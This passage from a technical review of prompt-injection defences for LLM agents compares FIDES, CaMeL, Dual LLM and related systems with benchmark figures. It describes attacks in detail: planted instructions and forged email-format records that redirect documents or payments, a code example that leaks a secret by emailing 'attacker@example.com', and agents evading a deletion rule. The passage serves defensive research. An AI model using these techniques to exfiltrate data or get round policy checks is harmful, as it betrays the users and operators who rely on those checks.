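In their tests, Costa and colleagues let an email through if it satisfied either of two rules. The integrity rule requires the decision to send it to be trusted, as it is here. The confidentiality rule requires every recipient to be allowed to read what the agent sends. The manager isn't, because the stranger wrote only to the office worker. FIDES would still send the summary, because satisfying the integrity rule is enough. Costa and colleagues reasoned that a user who asks for a disclosure in a trusted context intends it.

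If the stranger's email contained an order to forward the mailbox, the quarantined model would read it but the planner wouldn't. The quarantined model might write a false or empty summary, but it couldn't send anything. An agent that tracked labels without hiding the emails would also be safe, but it couldn't do this task. Its context would contain the stranger's text after the first step, so the policy would block the summary even if all three emails were harmless.

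The confidentiality rule also rejects messages that contain links from untrusted sources, but the either-or policy allows an email that passes either rule. A phishing link in the stranger's email could therefore reach the manager inside the summary.

Sometimes the planner has to know what an email says. Suppose the user wants a calendar event if any of the emails asks for a meeting. The planner can ask the quarantined model whether one does and restrict the answer to yes or no, a format enforced by the software running the model. The planner then reads the answer with a tool called `inspect`. FIDES records the format in the label, so a policy can be more lenient about an untrusted yes or no than about untrusted free text. A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit, and a choice among $n$ options at most $\log_2 n$ bits, which is too little to hold an instruction. The stranger can still cause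 a yes, and because the quarantined model then extracts the date and participants from his email, he can put a meeting of his choice in the calendar. He can't make the planner do something unrelated.

### How well FIDES works

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o and an attack that exploits knowledge of the agent's tools. Without policy checks, an ordinary agent carried out 152 injections, FIDES carried out 21, and a simpler design that permanently hides untrusted tool results carried out none. The paper's table contradicts the claim in its introduction that practical attacks succeeded against every design without checks. With the checks on, no design carried out any injections. These counts exclude some cases that AgentDojo scored as successful attacks, including tool calls that the policy had blocked and attacks that changed only the text of an answer.

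The checks also stopped honest work. The table shows the percentage of ordinary tasks completed when nobody was attacking:

| Design | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Ordinary agent with checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

Hiding untrusted text recovered much of the loss in three of the four settings. In the fourth, travel, the policy already allowed many of the actions, and GPT-4o often misused the variables. A stronger reasoning model, o1, handled them better, and with it FIDES completed 64.5% of office tasks, compared with 70.0% for an ordinary agent without checks.

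The perfect security result depends on how the researchers chose the labels. AgentDojo doesn't supply any, so they marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. An engineer labeling a real mailbox has no list of attacks to work from. The researchers also left the restricted answer formats out of the tests, because most AgentDojo tasks don't need them.

### Explicit secrecy and the flows it allows

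Costa and colleagues prove that label tracking can enforce a property called explicit secrecy. Let $g$ be the combined effect of one particular sequence of steps on all stored data, including anything outsiders can see. Write $d_1 =_L d_2$ if two versions of the data are the same in everything public. Explicit secrecy requires that for every sequence the agent might follow,

$$d_1 =_L d_2 \;\Rightarrow\; g(d_1) =_L g(d_2).$$

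If the agent takes the same steps, changing the secrets can't change what outsiders see. The proof treats the model as deterministic and ignores side channels such as timing.

But the secrets may leak by affecting which steps the agent takes, which is called an implicit flow. Suppose a policy accepts yes-or-no answers, and the office worker asks her assistant to check whether an email from the personnel department confirms her promotion. If it does, the assistant should open a car dealer's page on new cars, and otherwise the dealer's page on used cars. The assistant sends the dealer nothing from the email, and each sequence of steps has the same public effect whatever the email contains, so explicit secrecy holds. But the dealer can see which page the assistant opened, and anyone who knew about the instruction could infer from this whether she got the promotion.

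A stronger property, non-interference, would rule this out, but Costa and colleagues reject it because it would in effect forbid the agent to do anything publicly visible after reading anything secret. Their compromise is reasonable for preventing bulk data theft, since an attacker who learns one bit per decision needs many decisions to steal much. It is less reassuring when a single bit matters, such as whether someone was promoted or tested positive for a disease.

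### Tasks that require the agent to trust what it reads

For some tasks, no amount of hiding is enough. Let $S(d)$ be the set of action sequences that solve a task when the stored data is $d$. Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if one sequence works for all the data the agent might encounter:

$$\bigcap_{d \in D} S(d) \neq \varnothing$$

Sending a summary of three emails is a data-independent task because the agent makes the same calls whatever the emails contain. If the task is "Complete the tasks due today in my to-do app", the agent has to read the list before it can choose its actions, which makes the task data-dependent.

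Restricted answers help if a task depends on one small fact, such as whether somebody has asked for a meeting. They help less when the user wants the agent to follow instructions in a document. Many of AgentDojo's banking tasks require this, and FIDES blocked most of the resulting transactions, as its designers intended. Data-dependent tasks make up about 43% of the banking and Slack tasks but 5% of the office tasks. The office share is low partly because of which tasks the benchmark's designers chose. It would be much higher for a worker who delegates her to-do list every morning.

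If the office worker wants such a task done, somebody has to decide whose text may direct the assistant. The engineer might declare that files in one folder may determine payments because only the accounts department can write to that folder. This still relies on trust, but the assumption is no longer hidden, so a colleague can read and dispute it.

### Over-tainting and attempts to reduce it

Much of what trackers block in ordinary agents doesn't depend on untrusted data. For example, an assistant might read a newsletter and send an unrelated message an hour later in the same conversation. A cautious tracker labels that message as untrusted because the model had read the newsletter. Researchers call this "over-tainting" and the gradual spread of restrictive labels "label creep."

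Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, measured label creep in simulated teams of agents. The simulation used no language model. It generated random tasks of up to 20 interdependent tool calls, divided the calls among the agents and marked some of them as sensitive. An agent that made a sensitive call, or received or passed on material from one, kept the sensitive label from then on. The measure of harm was

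$$\mathcal{L} = \frac{\text{tool calls made with a sensitive label}}{\text{all tool calls}}.$$

Teams with more direct connections had a lower $\mathcal{L}$ because fewer agents had to relay sensitive material. Across nine arrangements, the share of possible connections that existed had a rank correlation of −0.96 with $\mathcal{L}$. When four of 20 calls were sensitive, $\mathcal{L}$ was about 5 percentage points higher with everything routed through a central agent than with exactly the connections each task needed. Giving the sensitive calls to a few specialised agents lowered $\mathcal{L}$, as did using more agents, but in well-connected teams the number of connections to monitor grew quadratically with the number of agents.

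Even the ideal arrangement didn't prevent label creep. The simulation had no way to relax a label, so the result shows the limits of rearranging agents, not of tracking in general. For the office assistant, the result suggests giving all web reading to the second agent, which would protect the actions that don't depend on that agent's reports.

Another approach is to estimate which inputs influenced a response. Costa and colleagues describe a method that identifies the influential messages, regenerates the response from those messages alone, and gives the new response only their labels. Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025) estimate in *RTBAS* that this would take 16 to 64 extra model calls with a typical lattice of four to six levels.

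Their own system, RTBAS, uses a screener to pick the parts of the conversation that seem relevant to the next step before the agent acts. The screener is either a second language model or a small neural network that uses attention, a measure of how strongly each part of the input affects the output. RTBAS combines the labels of the chosen parts and hides everything with a more restrictive label than the result. If the combined label breaks the policy for a tool call, RTBAS asks the user. A mistake by the screener therefore can't let hidden influence through. If it wrongly dismisses an untrusted email as irrelevant, the model doesn't see the email, and at worst the task fails.

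On AgentDojo, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated its policy. When there were no attacks, RTBAS with the language-model screener completed 10% fewer tasks than an undefended agent, and RTBAS with the attention screener completed 7.4% fewer. On banking tasks, the language-model screener roughly doubled both running time and cost. Completion rates on the Slack tasks were only 22% and 33%, because many of them require acting on text from untrusted websites. Zhong and colleagues consider those tasks inherently unsafe without the user's confirmation.

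*GIF* (Storek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) replaces the yes-or-no judgement of relevance with an upper bound on how much information can pass from a stretch of text to, for example, the recipient field of an email. The method, geometric information flow, calculates this bound from the model's Jacobian, a matrix that describes how small changes in the input change the output. The paper reports near-perfect recall on tests of prompt injection and data leakage. Measurements from small models also carried over to models up to 200 times larger, so an engineer might be able to use the method without access to a commercial model's internals.

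A computer-checked proof supports the bound, but only for inputs close to the text the model read. The bound therefore suits a defender examining a hostile email as it arrives. It is less suitable for finding trust assumptions from ordinary mail, because a harmless email may have little influence on the recipient field even when a hostile email in the same place would have a lot.

### Checking individual values

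The remedies above are meant to make the labels more accurate. An engineer can instead change what the rule checks. The integrity rule in FIDES checks whether the agent decided to act in a trusted context, but the engineer often needs to know whether one particular value, such as the recipient's address, came from someone entitled to choose it.

Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, built FORGE, which records every message, tool call and result in a graph with arrows to whatever they may have influenced. Before each action, it evaluates rules over the graph. One of the rules in their provenance policy amounts to

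$$\text{deny}(a) \leftarrow \text{sends}(a) \wedge \text{tainted}(a) \wedge \text{destination}(a, v) \wedge \neg\,\text{anchored}(v).$$

After an agent has been exposed to untrusted text, FORGE lets it send something only to an anchored destination, meaning one that comes from the user's request, a record the operator maintains or another trusted source. Other rules require the user to have asked for that kind of action, such as a deletion, and for that particular target.

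They compared this policy with the FIDES policy on AgentDojo, using GPT-4o. In the runs below, the scaffold also repeated the user's request after each batch of tool results, which alone makes injections less effective.

| Rules | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% |
| FIDES policy | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.6% |
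| Provenance policy | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.9% |

The agent completed nearly twice as many tasks under the provenance policy, at about the same level of security. But the comparison is unfair to FIDES as a whole, because Palumbo and colleagues applied the FIDES policy to AgentDojo's standard agent, without the variables that keep untrusted text out of the context. With GPT-4o, the complete FIDES design completed about 52% of tasks when the results from Costa and colleagues are weighted by the number of tasks in each setting. The agent completed 57.3% under the provenance policy when the scaffold didn't repeat the request, so the policy's advantage is probably much smaller than it appears in the table. An engineer could also combine the two ideas by hiding untrusted text and checking individual values.

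The policies also differ in what they check, which matters more for finding assumptions. The generic FIDES policies check the label of the decision to act and ignore the integrity labels of the values. If the office worker asks her assistant to pay a bill, the decision is trusted because it is hers, and the account number can pass from the bill to the payment inside a variable. FIDES would therefore allow payment of a forged bill. Its labels contain the information needed to prevent this, and Costa and colleagues mention a stricter policy that requires a trusted recipient, but somebody has to write it. The provenance policy would block the payment unless the account number was already in a trusted record, and the blocked payment would alert the engineer to assumption 4.

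Precise rules are difficult to write. When a user asks an agent to delete the largest file, the file's name comes from a listing, not from her request. Palumbo and colleagues added a rule that allows the agent to delete only the largest file in the listing. Agents found they could get around it by listing the files again after the deletion, which made the next file the largest, or by running a search that returned only the attacker's file. A further rule now blocks the deletion if any listing in the context shows a different file as the largest.

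### From blocking to finding

To find assumptions with a tracker, an engineer can run it in log-only mode, so that it records violations without stopping the agent. She labels the sources, writes a strict policy and lets the assistant do a week of ordinary work. For each violation, the log records which source influenced which action. She then asks what would have to be true of the source for the action to be safe. If the assistant took a recipient's address from the body of a supplier's email, the answer is assumption 4. If it sent mail relying on a saved note that contained text from a stranger's message, the answer is assumption 7.

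Tracking untrusted data can reveal hidden trust assumptions even when there is no attacker. Costa and colleagues examined the ordinary tasks that FIDES had failed and found that many banking tasks involved following instructions in a file. In effect, they had discovered that the bank agent trusted whoever wrote the file.

Palumbo and colleagues give two clearer examples. In the first, a team of agents assessing drug safety was required to get a supervisor's approval before querying a government database. In 15 runs without enforcement, the agents made 40 unapproved queries and still reached the correct conclusion every time. In the second, the researchers reviewed 1,368 recorded customer-service conversations and found 17 in which the agent looked up product information before establishing the customer's identity. Of these, 13 had received full marks from the benchmark. An engineer who checked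 only whether the tasks succeeded would have missed both problems.

Recorded runs need to show what influenced each action, and several tools can reconstruct this. *AgentArmor* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2025) turns an agent's activity into the kind of graph that compilers use to analyse programs. Arrows connect the user's request, tool results and the parameters of later calls, and a registry adds information about each tool and the data it handles. The researchers designed it to block attacks, and report that it reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo to 3%, with agents completing only about 1% fewer tasks. The graph would also let an engineer trace an address in an outgoing email back to where the assistant found it.

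Agent-Sentry is a defence that learns an agent's normal behaviour from past runs. If the assistant has always copied addresses from emails, Agent-Sentry treats this as normal and won't raise an alarm. The engineer would therefore learn more from the behaviour it has accepted as normal than from its warnings.

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) presents NeuroTaint, a tool built for auditing recorded runs. It checks the arguments of each sensitive call for untrusted content. It searches first for unique markers it attached to incoming text, then for shared strings, and then for passages with a similar meaning, so it can recognise a paraphrase. When the agent writes to memory, NeuroTaint saves labels with the entry and restores them when the agent reads it again, even in a later session.

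If none of this finds a match, NeuroTaint uses a language model to predict whether the agent would still have made the call if the suspicious text had been replaced with neutral text such as "No relevant information found". This is close to the definition of trust given earlier, but it relies on a model's prediction instead of repeated runs.

Cai and colleagues give the example of a planted search result that makes an agent send its research to an attacker's server instead of running a program. The attacker's web address passes from the search result into the call, so a text search would find it, although they present the example as influence that leaves no trace in the data. A better example would be an email that persuades the agent to delete a file it already knew about.

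NeuroTaint had an F1 score of 92.8% on a benchmark of 400 scenarios that the researchers wrote themselves, and their version of FIDES scored 52.2%. Half of the scenarios contained a real flow from an untrusted source to a sensitive call. The comparison is a weak test of FIDES, which is meant to block actions, not to establish whether content really passed between two points. The version they tested also raised no alarms in four of the 20 agent frameworks, which accounts for 40 of its 92 misses. Engineers will only read a log if most of its entries are worth reading, so the better evidence for NeuroTaint is that it correctly cleared 184 of the 200 scenarios without a real flow.

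A log contains only what happened while the tracker was running. If nobody sends the office worker a calendar invitation that week, the log won't show whether the assistant trusts invitations. What the log contains also depends on the model. When Cai and colleagues ran their scenarios with Claude Opus 4.6 instead of GPT-4.1 mini, the share of flows that NeuroTaint reported fell from 93.5% to 54.7%. They attribute the drop partly to the stronger model refusing suspicious requests before it reached the sensitive call. A log of completed flows would not show that the agent's safety in those cases depended on the model's refusal.

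### What tracking takes on trust

A tracker can't detect that a label is wrong. In one RTBAS test, text containing a possible injection was labeled as the user's own writing, so RTBAS didn't track it. The office worker could cause the same problem by forwarding a stranger's email to herself. If the tracker labels mail by sender, it would label the stranger's words as hers.

FIDES's banking tests hid the descriptions of transactions but treated the amounts and dates as trusted. One task was to change the user's password if there was a suspicious transaction. The agent considered a large amount suspicious and changed the password, and the policy allowed this because the agent had read only trusted data. Labeling the amount as trusted was itself a trust assumption, since anyone who can send the user money can choose the amount. AgentDojo's attacks did not test this assumption.

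It is also unclear who should assign the labels. Zhong and colleagues leave this to the agent's developers and acknowledge that it is a burden. Costa and colleagues infer an email's readers from its address fields, although somebody may have shared it more widely. For integrity labels, they suggest mail servers could authenticate senders' addresses with DMARC, a standard for detecting forged sender domains. In *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, Wang, Li and Tian (2026) examined 21 agent products, including Claude Code and Cursor. As of April 2026, none let users label data by how much they trusted it, although eight academic papers had proposed such labelling. Wang and colleagues think users find it hard to reason about where data came from. Their count covers features users can see, so some companies may track labels internally.

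Besides tool descriptions, FIDES treats user and system messages as trusted, so if a user pastes a web page into a request, the page's text is trusted as much as the user's own words. FIDES also assumes that tools behave as their labels imply. Zhong and colleagues describe a pair of tools that violates this assumption. One is allowed to send private messages, and the other returns sent messages labelled as public, so an agent could remove the private label from a secret by sending it to the user and reading it back.

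Finally, FORGE's guarantee holds only if every relevant action passes through its checks and its graph contains every relevant influence. A program that opens its own network connection can bypass the checks, and if the graph lacks an arrow for an influence, FORGE misses that influence.

### Which of the eight assumptions tracking exposes

Tracking is best at exposing assumption 1, that an email's text is information and not an order. The tracker records every consequential step the assistant takes after its planner has read an email, even if the email was harmless. Many of these records will be false positives because of over-tainting. Tracking exposes assumption 4, about extracted values, only if the policy checks individual values.

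For assumptions 6 and 7, a message from the second agent must carry the labels of everything that agent has read, and a stored note must keep the label of the email it came from. If the software drops these labels, the tracker will treat a stranger's words as trusted.

Reader sets can expose assumption 3, which static analysis could not. If someone has recorded that only the personnel department may read the salary file, sending it to anyone else, even a genuine colleague, breaks the confidentiality rule. The either-or policy would still allow this if the office worker herself asked the agent to send the file, so an engineer looking for assumptions should log violations of each rule separately.

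Tracking exposes assumption 8 for tools that fetch web pages, if the policy treats the requested address as outgoing data. Tracking misses images and links in the assistant's answers because FIDES doesn't check answers by default and the FORGE tests didn't check them either.

Assumption 2, that the displayed sender is real, comes up when an engineer decides how to label mail from a colleague's address. If she labels the mail trusted because of the address, tracking won't reveal the assumption later. Tracking with FIDES can't expose assumption 5, because tool descriptions start with the most trusted label.

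## Designs that keep untrusted text away from the planner

An engineer can build an agent whose planner never reads untrusted text. FIDES and an older design called Dual LLM both do this with variables. In Dual LLM, one model plans and another reads the untrusted text. This protects the plan but not the values the plan uses, such as an email address from a document. CaMeL, a later design from Google DeepMind, also checks where each value came from before a tool receives it. These checks require someone to decide whose data may fill each argument of each tool, and writing those decisions down can reveal trust assumptions before the agent runs.

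### The Dual LLM pattern

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes an assistant with three parts. A privileged model acts as the planner and can call tools, but it reads only trusted text, mostly the user's requests. A quarantined model reads emails and web pages and has no tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, runs the tools and passes data between the models.

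As in FIDES, the planner handles outside text only by variable name. To summarise the user's latest email, it has the controller store the email as `$VAR1`, pass it to the quarantined model, store the summary as `$VAR2` and display it.

Willison made one exception, allowing the planner to read an answer that the controller has matched to a fixed set of categories. The restricted answers in FIDES are similar.

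He called his own solution "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the planner undoes the protection. It also assumes nobody will trick the user into pasting hostile text into a request.

### How a safe plan can send a document to an attacker

DeepMind's researchers found another flaw. Willison (2025) explains it with their example in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. A user asks her assistant to send Bob the document he requested in their last meeting, and adds that his address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The planner writes five steps: find the notes, extract the document's name, extract Bob's address, fetch the document and send it.

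Text in the notes can't add steps to the plan or change their order. But the quarantined model has to read the notes to find the address, and anyone who can write in them can plant an instruction to return a different address. The controller then follows the plan exactly and sends the document to the attacker.

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a design that would prevent this for some requests. In its example, which Willison (2025) retells in a post of the same name, a user wants to send today's schedule to her boss, John Doe. Before reading anything, the planner writes one call that reads the calendar and another that emails the result to John's address. A hostile calendar entry can change the body of the email but not the recipient, because the address is already in the plan. This design wouldn't help with Bob, because his address is in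 the notes.

The paper presents six designs, which differ in how much outsiders' text can influence the agent's actions. In the strictest, the model chooses an action but never sees the result, so outsiders' text can't affect its choices. In another, an agent that collects invoices gives each file to a separate model, which may return only whether the file is relevant. Hostile text in a file can cause that file to be included but can't have any other effect. An engineer who chooses one of these designs also chooses which trust assumptions to accept.

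### CaMeL, line by line

In CaMeL, the planner turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and tags every value with a capability, which records the value's sources and who may read it. Values computed from other values inherit their capabilities, much as labels combine in FIDES. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, which *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes as a function that takes the call, its arguments and their capabilities, and returns allow or deny.

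Willison gives a short program that emails Bob a reminder. A similar program for the document might be:

```python
notes = get_latest_notes()
title = query_quarantined_llm(
    "Find the document Bob asked for in [notes]",
    output_schema=str)
address = query_quarantined_llm(
    "Find Bob's email address in [notes]",
    output_schema=EmailStr)
document = fetch_document(title)
send_email(recipient=address,
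           subject="The document you wanted",
           attachment=document)
```

Suppose an outside contractor, the office worker and Bob can all edit the notes, but only the office worker and Bob may read the document.

1. `notes`: The policy always allows the assistant to read notes. The interpreter records all three people as possible sources and as permitted readers.
2. `title`: The quarantined model extracts the document's name. The name inherits the capability of the notes, so the contractor is among its possible sources.
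3. `address`: The address inherits the same capability. The interpreter rejects any answer that isn't in the form of an email address, which leaves little room for an instruction. It can't tell whether the address is Bob's.
4. `document`: The file brings its own list of readers, the office worker and Bob. Its sources now include the authors of the notes, because the title determined which file the assistant fetched.
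5. `send_email`: The planner wrote the subject line itself, so that is trusted. The recipient isn't, because the contractor may have supplied it. In Willison's example, the policy allows an email only to a trusted recipient, and otherwise the system can ask the user to approve it.

A policy could also check the list of readers and allow the email if the recipient already has access to the document. Bob's real address would pass without the user being asked, and the contractor's would fail.

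### Rules for each argument

In an ordinary agent, the recipient of an email can be any text, and nobody needs to have an opinion about where it comes from. A CaMeL policy for `send_email` can't protect the recipient until somebody has decided who may choose it. For the office assistant, an engineer might write these rules:

| Argument | Rule | What the rule relies on |
|---|---|---|
| Recipient of an email | Must come from the user's request or her contacts | Outsiders can't add contacts |
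| Attachment | The recipient must already be allowed to read it | The file's sharing list is correct |
| Address of a web page | Must contain no private data | The tags identify all private data |
| Question to the second agent | Must contain no private data | The same, and the agent doesn't have private data already |
| Text of a saved note | Must come from the user | She didn't paste it from somewhere else |

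The last column shows that the rules still require some trust, but they replace a vague reliance on "the email" or "the notes" with a narrower claim that a colleague can check.

Some designs put the rule about what an agent may trust in the tool's definition. In *Language-Based Agent Control*, Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026) built an agent that compiles bibliographies and may use only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that writes to the bibliography accepts only values of a type called `Trusted Bib`, and only the DBLP lookup can create one, so anyone who reads the function's definition can see that the agent trusts only DBLP. If the agent writes a program that makes up an entry, the type checker rejects the program before it runs. In 100 tasks, an ordinary agent with web search got 19 of 1,002 citations wrong, while this agent got none of 925 wrong.

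Switching on CaMeL's policies shows how much ordinary work depends on untrusted data. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks with no attacker. It completed 67% of them with one model and 71% with another when the policies were off, and 37.5% with either model when they were on. In the Slack setting, Zhou and colleagues found that the policies reduced the number of tasks CaMeL completed, out of 21, from 13–17 to 4–6, depending on the model. Most of the lost tasks were probably ones in which an outsider's data had filled an argument that the policies protect. An engineer could examine the newly blocked tasks in the same way as a tracker's log.

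But both teams could run CaMeL without policies, so the architecture doesn't require developers to write any. A developer who adopts the planner and the quarantined model but skips the policies could still have the flaw in the Bob example, with no record of it.

### Who writes the rules

The CaMeL paper, as quoted by Willison, acknowledges that users have to specify and maintain the policies. This worries him because he still struggles with Amazon's cloud permission system after two decades in application security.

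The model can write the policies itself, which saves work. *CapLite* (2026) tested this with 15 small models, each writing policies for its own agent. The policies let through 676 attacks across 14 of the models. During attacks, they also blocked between 25% and 77% of the calls that would have changed something, and ordinary task completion fell from 59.4% to 43.8%. When the same models ran CaMeL with policies written by its creators, only 20 of 13,935 attacks succeeded, 17 of them with a single model. Failure rates showed no clear trend with capability in these tests, though larger models may write better policies. An engineer would still have to read a policy, even a good one, to learn anything from it.

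Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, the LLMbda calculus, in which a program must use the word `endorse` to treat an untrusted value as trusted, so exceptions to the rules are easy to find. For example, an agent might sort a stranger's email into one of a few fixed categories and endorse the category for use as the subject of a reply. Their agent, Randori, completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2 while its checks were on. With two other models, forbidding endorsement cut the completion rate by 10 to 13 percentage points.

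Searching Randori's programs for `endorse` would be a good way to start an audit, because it would list the places where the agent relies on untrusted data. The planner, a language model, writes these endorsements before the agent has read anything hostile. This limits an attacker's influence, but no person has agreed that the data deserves trust.

Designers can also ask the user to decide the hard cases. Willison predicted in 2023 that users would learn to click "OK" as fast as possible, and Wang and colleagues' survey of agent products describes how companies have tried to reduce the number of approval requests. Anthropic reports that Claude Code makes 84% fewer requests when it can run commands inside a restricted environment without approval. Other products offer an "always allow" button, which Wang and colleagues warn silently widens what the agent trusts. Users usually click it while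 trying to finish something else, and each click creates a trust assumption.

Some products have the user approve a whole plan instead of each step. That works badly for the Bob request, because the plan contains `recipient=address` and the address isn't known yet. The office worker would approve a sensible plan, and the document would go to the contractor.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) shows why an approval should cover the exact arguments. Suppose Alice approves a reply, but her approval permits the next email whatever it contains. A hostile message could make the model email her private data before it sends the reply. That email would use up the approval, so the monitor would then block the reply she wanted. If the approval covers only the exact text and recipient, the model can't send the private data unless that email happens to be identical to the approved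 reply.

Finally, a policy rule can restate a hidden trust assumption without testing it. Suppose the policy blocks every address that comes from meeting notes, users complain, and the engineer declares the notes trusted. The assistant now behaves as it did before she installed CaMeL. Her assumption that the notes are safe is now written down, but it is just as likely to be false.

Rules that are each sensible can also be unsafe in combination. *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks and defences, lists this among CaMeL's limitations. For example, one rule might let the assistant save documents to a shared folder, and another might let it invite people to the folder. Together, the two rules would let the assistant give a document to someone who shouldn't have it.

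### Leaks that formal analysis found in CaMeL

Garby and colleagues studied CaMeL's interpreter and found that it can lose track of a secret when a program skips a step. Their example is a version of a classic problem from the 1970s. A program along these lines would reveal whether a customer is rich:

```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
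if rich:
    send_email("attacker@example.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the program sets `tmp` to false, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as depending on the secret. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`, so `rich` stays true, CaMeL doesn't mark it, and the policy allows the email. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes false and the program sends no email. The attacker can therefore learn whether the balance is above the threshold from whether an email arrives.

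An attacker would have trouble getting CaMeL's planner to write this program, because the planner reads only the user's request. Another error that Garby and colleagues found could do harm in an ordinary program, and it is a hidden trust assumption in CaMeL itself. When a program inserts an untrusted value into text, CaMeL treats the result as trusted. Suppose the program builds an address by putting a name from a stranger's email in front of `@company.com`. The policy would accept the address even though the stranger chose the recipient.

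CaMeL can also leak data outside its interpreter. If a policy blocks a program, CaMeL tries again in an ordinary Python loop, where nothing tracks the data. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit, and many attempts could reveal the whole secret. Randori avoids this by testing its program in a simulated world until it works before running it on real data.

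Garby and colleagues use the proof checker Lean to prove that programs in their language can't leak secrets in these ways, although an observer may still learn something from whether a program finishes. The guarantee depends on someone labelling the sources correctly and putting checks on the tools that matter.

Dongol analyses designs of this kind without assuming anything about the user's privacy preferences. He compares an agent with an imaginary reference agent that runs the same plan but never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is secure if it reveals nothing about the user's data to an attacker that the reference agent wouldn't also reveal. For example, an assistant that sends the user's calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting passes even if an injection triggers the reply, because a genuine request would have revealed the same thing. It fails if the injection also extracts a password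 reset code.

By this standard, Dual LLM without tags leaks and a version with tags is secure. But a plan can leak even with tags if its next step depends on the quarantined model's answer. Many ordinary requests need such a plan, for example "if the email asks for a meeting, send my calendar".

### Checking the program before it runs

CaMeL checks values while a program runs. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, have the agent write its programs in Scala 3, whose compiler can check them before they run. In their system, TACIT, "capability" has an older meaning than it does in CaMeL. It is an object in the program that gives any code that holds it permission to do something, such as read one folder. The compiler works out which capabilities each part of the program can use.

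TACIT puts secret files in a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent can apply a function to the contents only if the compiler confirms that the function has no way to send, save or print anything. The result stays in the wrapper, so a program can't use a secret to decide whether to send an email, as it did in the CaMeL leak.

Odersky and colleagues ran 131 trials with each of two models, mostly ordinary tasks with planted attacks. When the files were in the wrapper, no secret reached the agent's output. Without the wrapper, secrets reached the output in 1.5% of trials with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 8.4% with MiniMax M2.5.

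TACIT is better at recording who may read data than who may have written it. The agent may read untrusted text before it writes its next program, and a function that takes a recipient as ordinary text will accept a stranger's address. To protect the recipient, an engineer would have to define a special type for it, as Zhou and colleagues did for bibliography entries. TACIT's shared code is about 1,000 lines, and describing the tools for each new kind of work took a few hundred more in two tests.

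Zhou and colleagues compared their own system, ELBA, with CaMeL on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks and 105 attacks. ELBA agents write programs in Haskell, and they can keep using tools after reading untrusted text, but the text's label then restricts what they may do. The table gives the range of tasks completed across four models when nobody was attacking:

| System | Policies off | Policies on |
|---|---|---|
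| CaMeL | 13–17 of 21 | 4–6 of 21 |
| ELBA | 14–18 of 21 | 8–10 of 21 |

ELBA completed more tasks under its policies but took about three times as long to run. Both systems resisted all 105 attacks with every model, even with their policies off, so the attacks revealed no difference between them. An engineer who looked only at this result might conclude that the policies were unnecessary.

To find out what the policies contributed, Zhou and colleagues altered ELBA so that any model that read a planted instruction received it as its task. Without policies, up to 42% of the attacks then succeeded, depending on the model. With policies, none of the 735 attempts per model succeeded, but the agents also completed far fewer tasks. The test shows that the perfect scores without policies had depended on a trust assumption, that the models would ignore planted instructions. It doesn't show whether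 ELBA or CaMeL is safer, because the researchers didn't run it on CaMeL.

Separating the planner from untrusted text stops many attacks by itself. Garby and colleagues sorted the 144 combinations of task and attack in the banking setting and found that in 97, the attack needed a step that no sensible plan for the task would contain. But they also found that when the task was to read a file and follow its instructions, CaMeL's planner sometimes wrote a program that called whichever tool the file named. With policies off, an attacker who had changed the file could then choose the tool.

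### False text that contains no order

The separation protects the planner from instructions in untrusted text, but an attacker can often succeed with a false statement instead. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) studies text that imitates the format in which tools return data. In one example, the body of a stranger's email contains text that looks like the start of another email, from someone the user knows. The mail program treats it all as one message from the stranger, but a language model may see two messages and believe the second sender is genuine.

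The imitation doesn't have to be exact. Across six models, 31% to 43% of such attacks succeeded on data in JSON, a common format for tool results, even though the tool had marked the attacker's punctuation as ordinary text. Defences that kept the success rate of planted instructions below 1% let through up to 50% of these attacks.

Dual LLM doesn't prevent attacks that use false records, because the quarantined model reads the record and passes its contents to the planner as fact. The planner then uses the false information in exactly the plan the user wanted. According to Choi and colleagues, tracking where each value came from, as CaMeL does, can stop these attacks if the rules are detailed enough. But they warn that such rules are hard to write and that such precise tracking often prevents the agent from doing useful work.

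Asking the user doesn't reliably help either. Choi and colleagues made three coding agents mistake an outsider's comment for advice from a project's maintainer. The agents asked for approval before running the command the comment suggested, but they explained that the maintainer had recommended it. A user who trusted that explanation would have approved the command.

An attacker doesn't need to imitate a format if the user has asked the agent to rely on a document. Only two of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded. In both, the user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The CaMeL paper reports the same kind of failure and treats it as outside the threats CaMeL was meant to stop. A capability can show that an account number came from the file, but not whether the number is right. To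 find out, somebody has to compare it with another record or call the supplier.

### Which of the eight assumptions these designs expose

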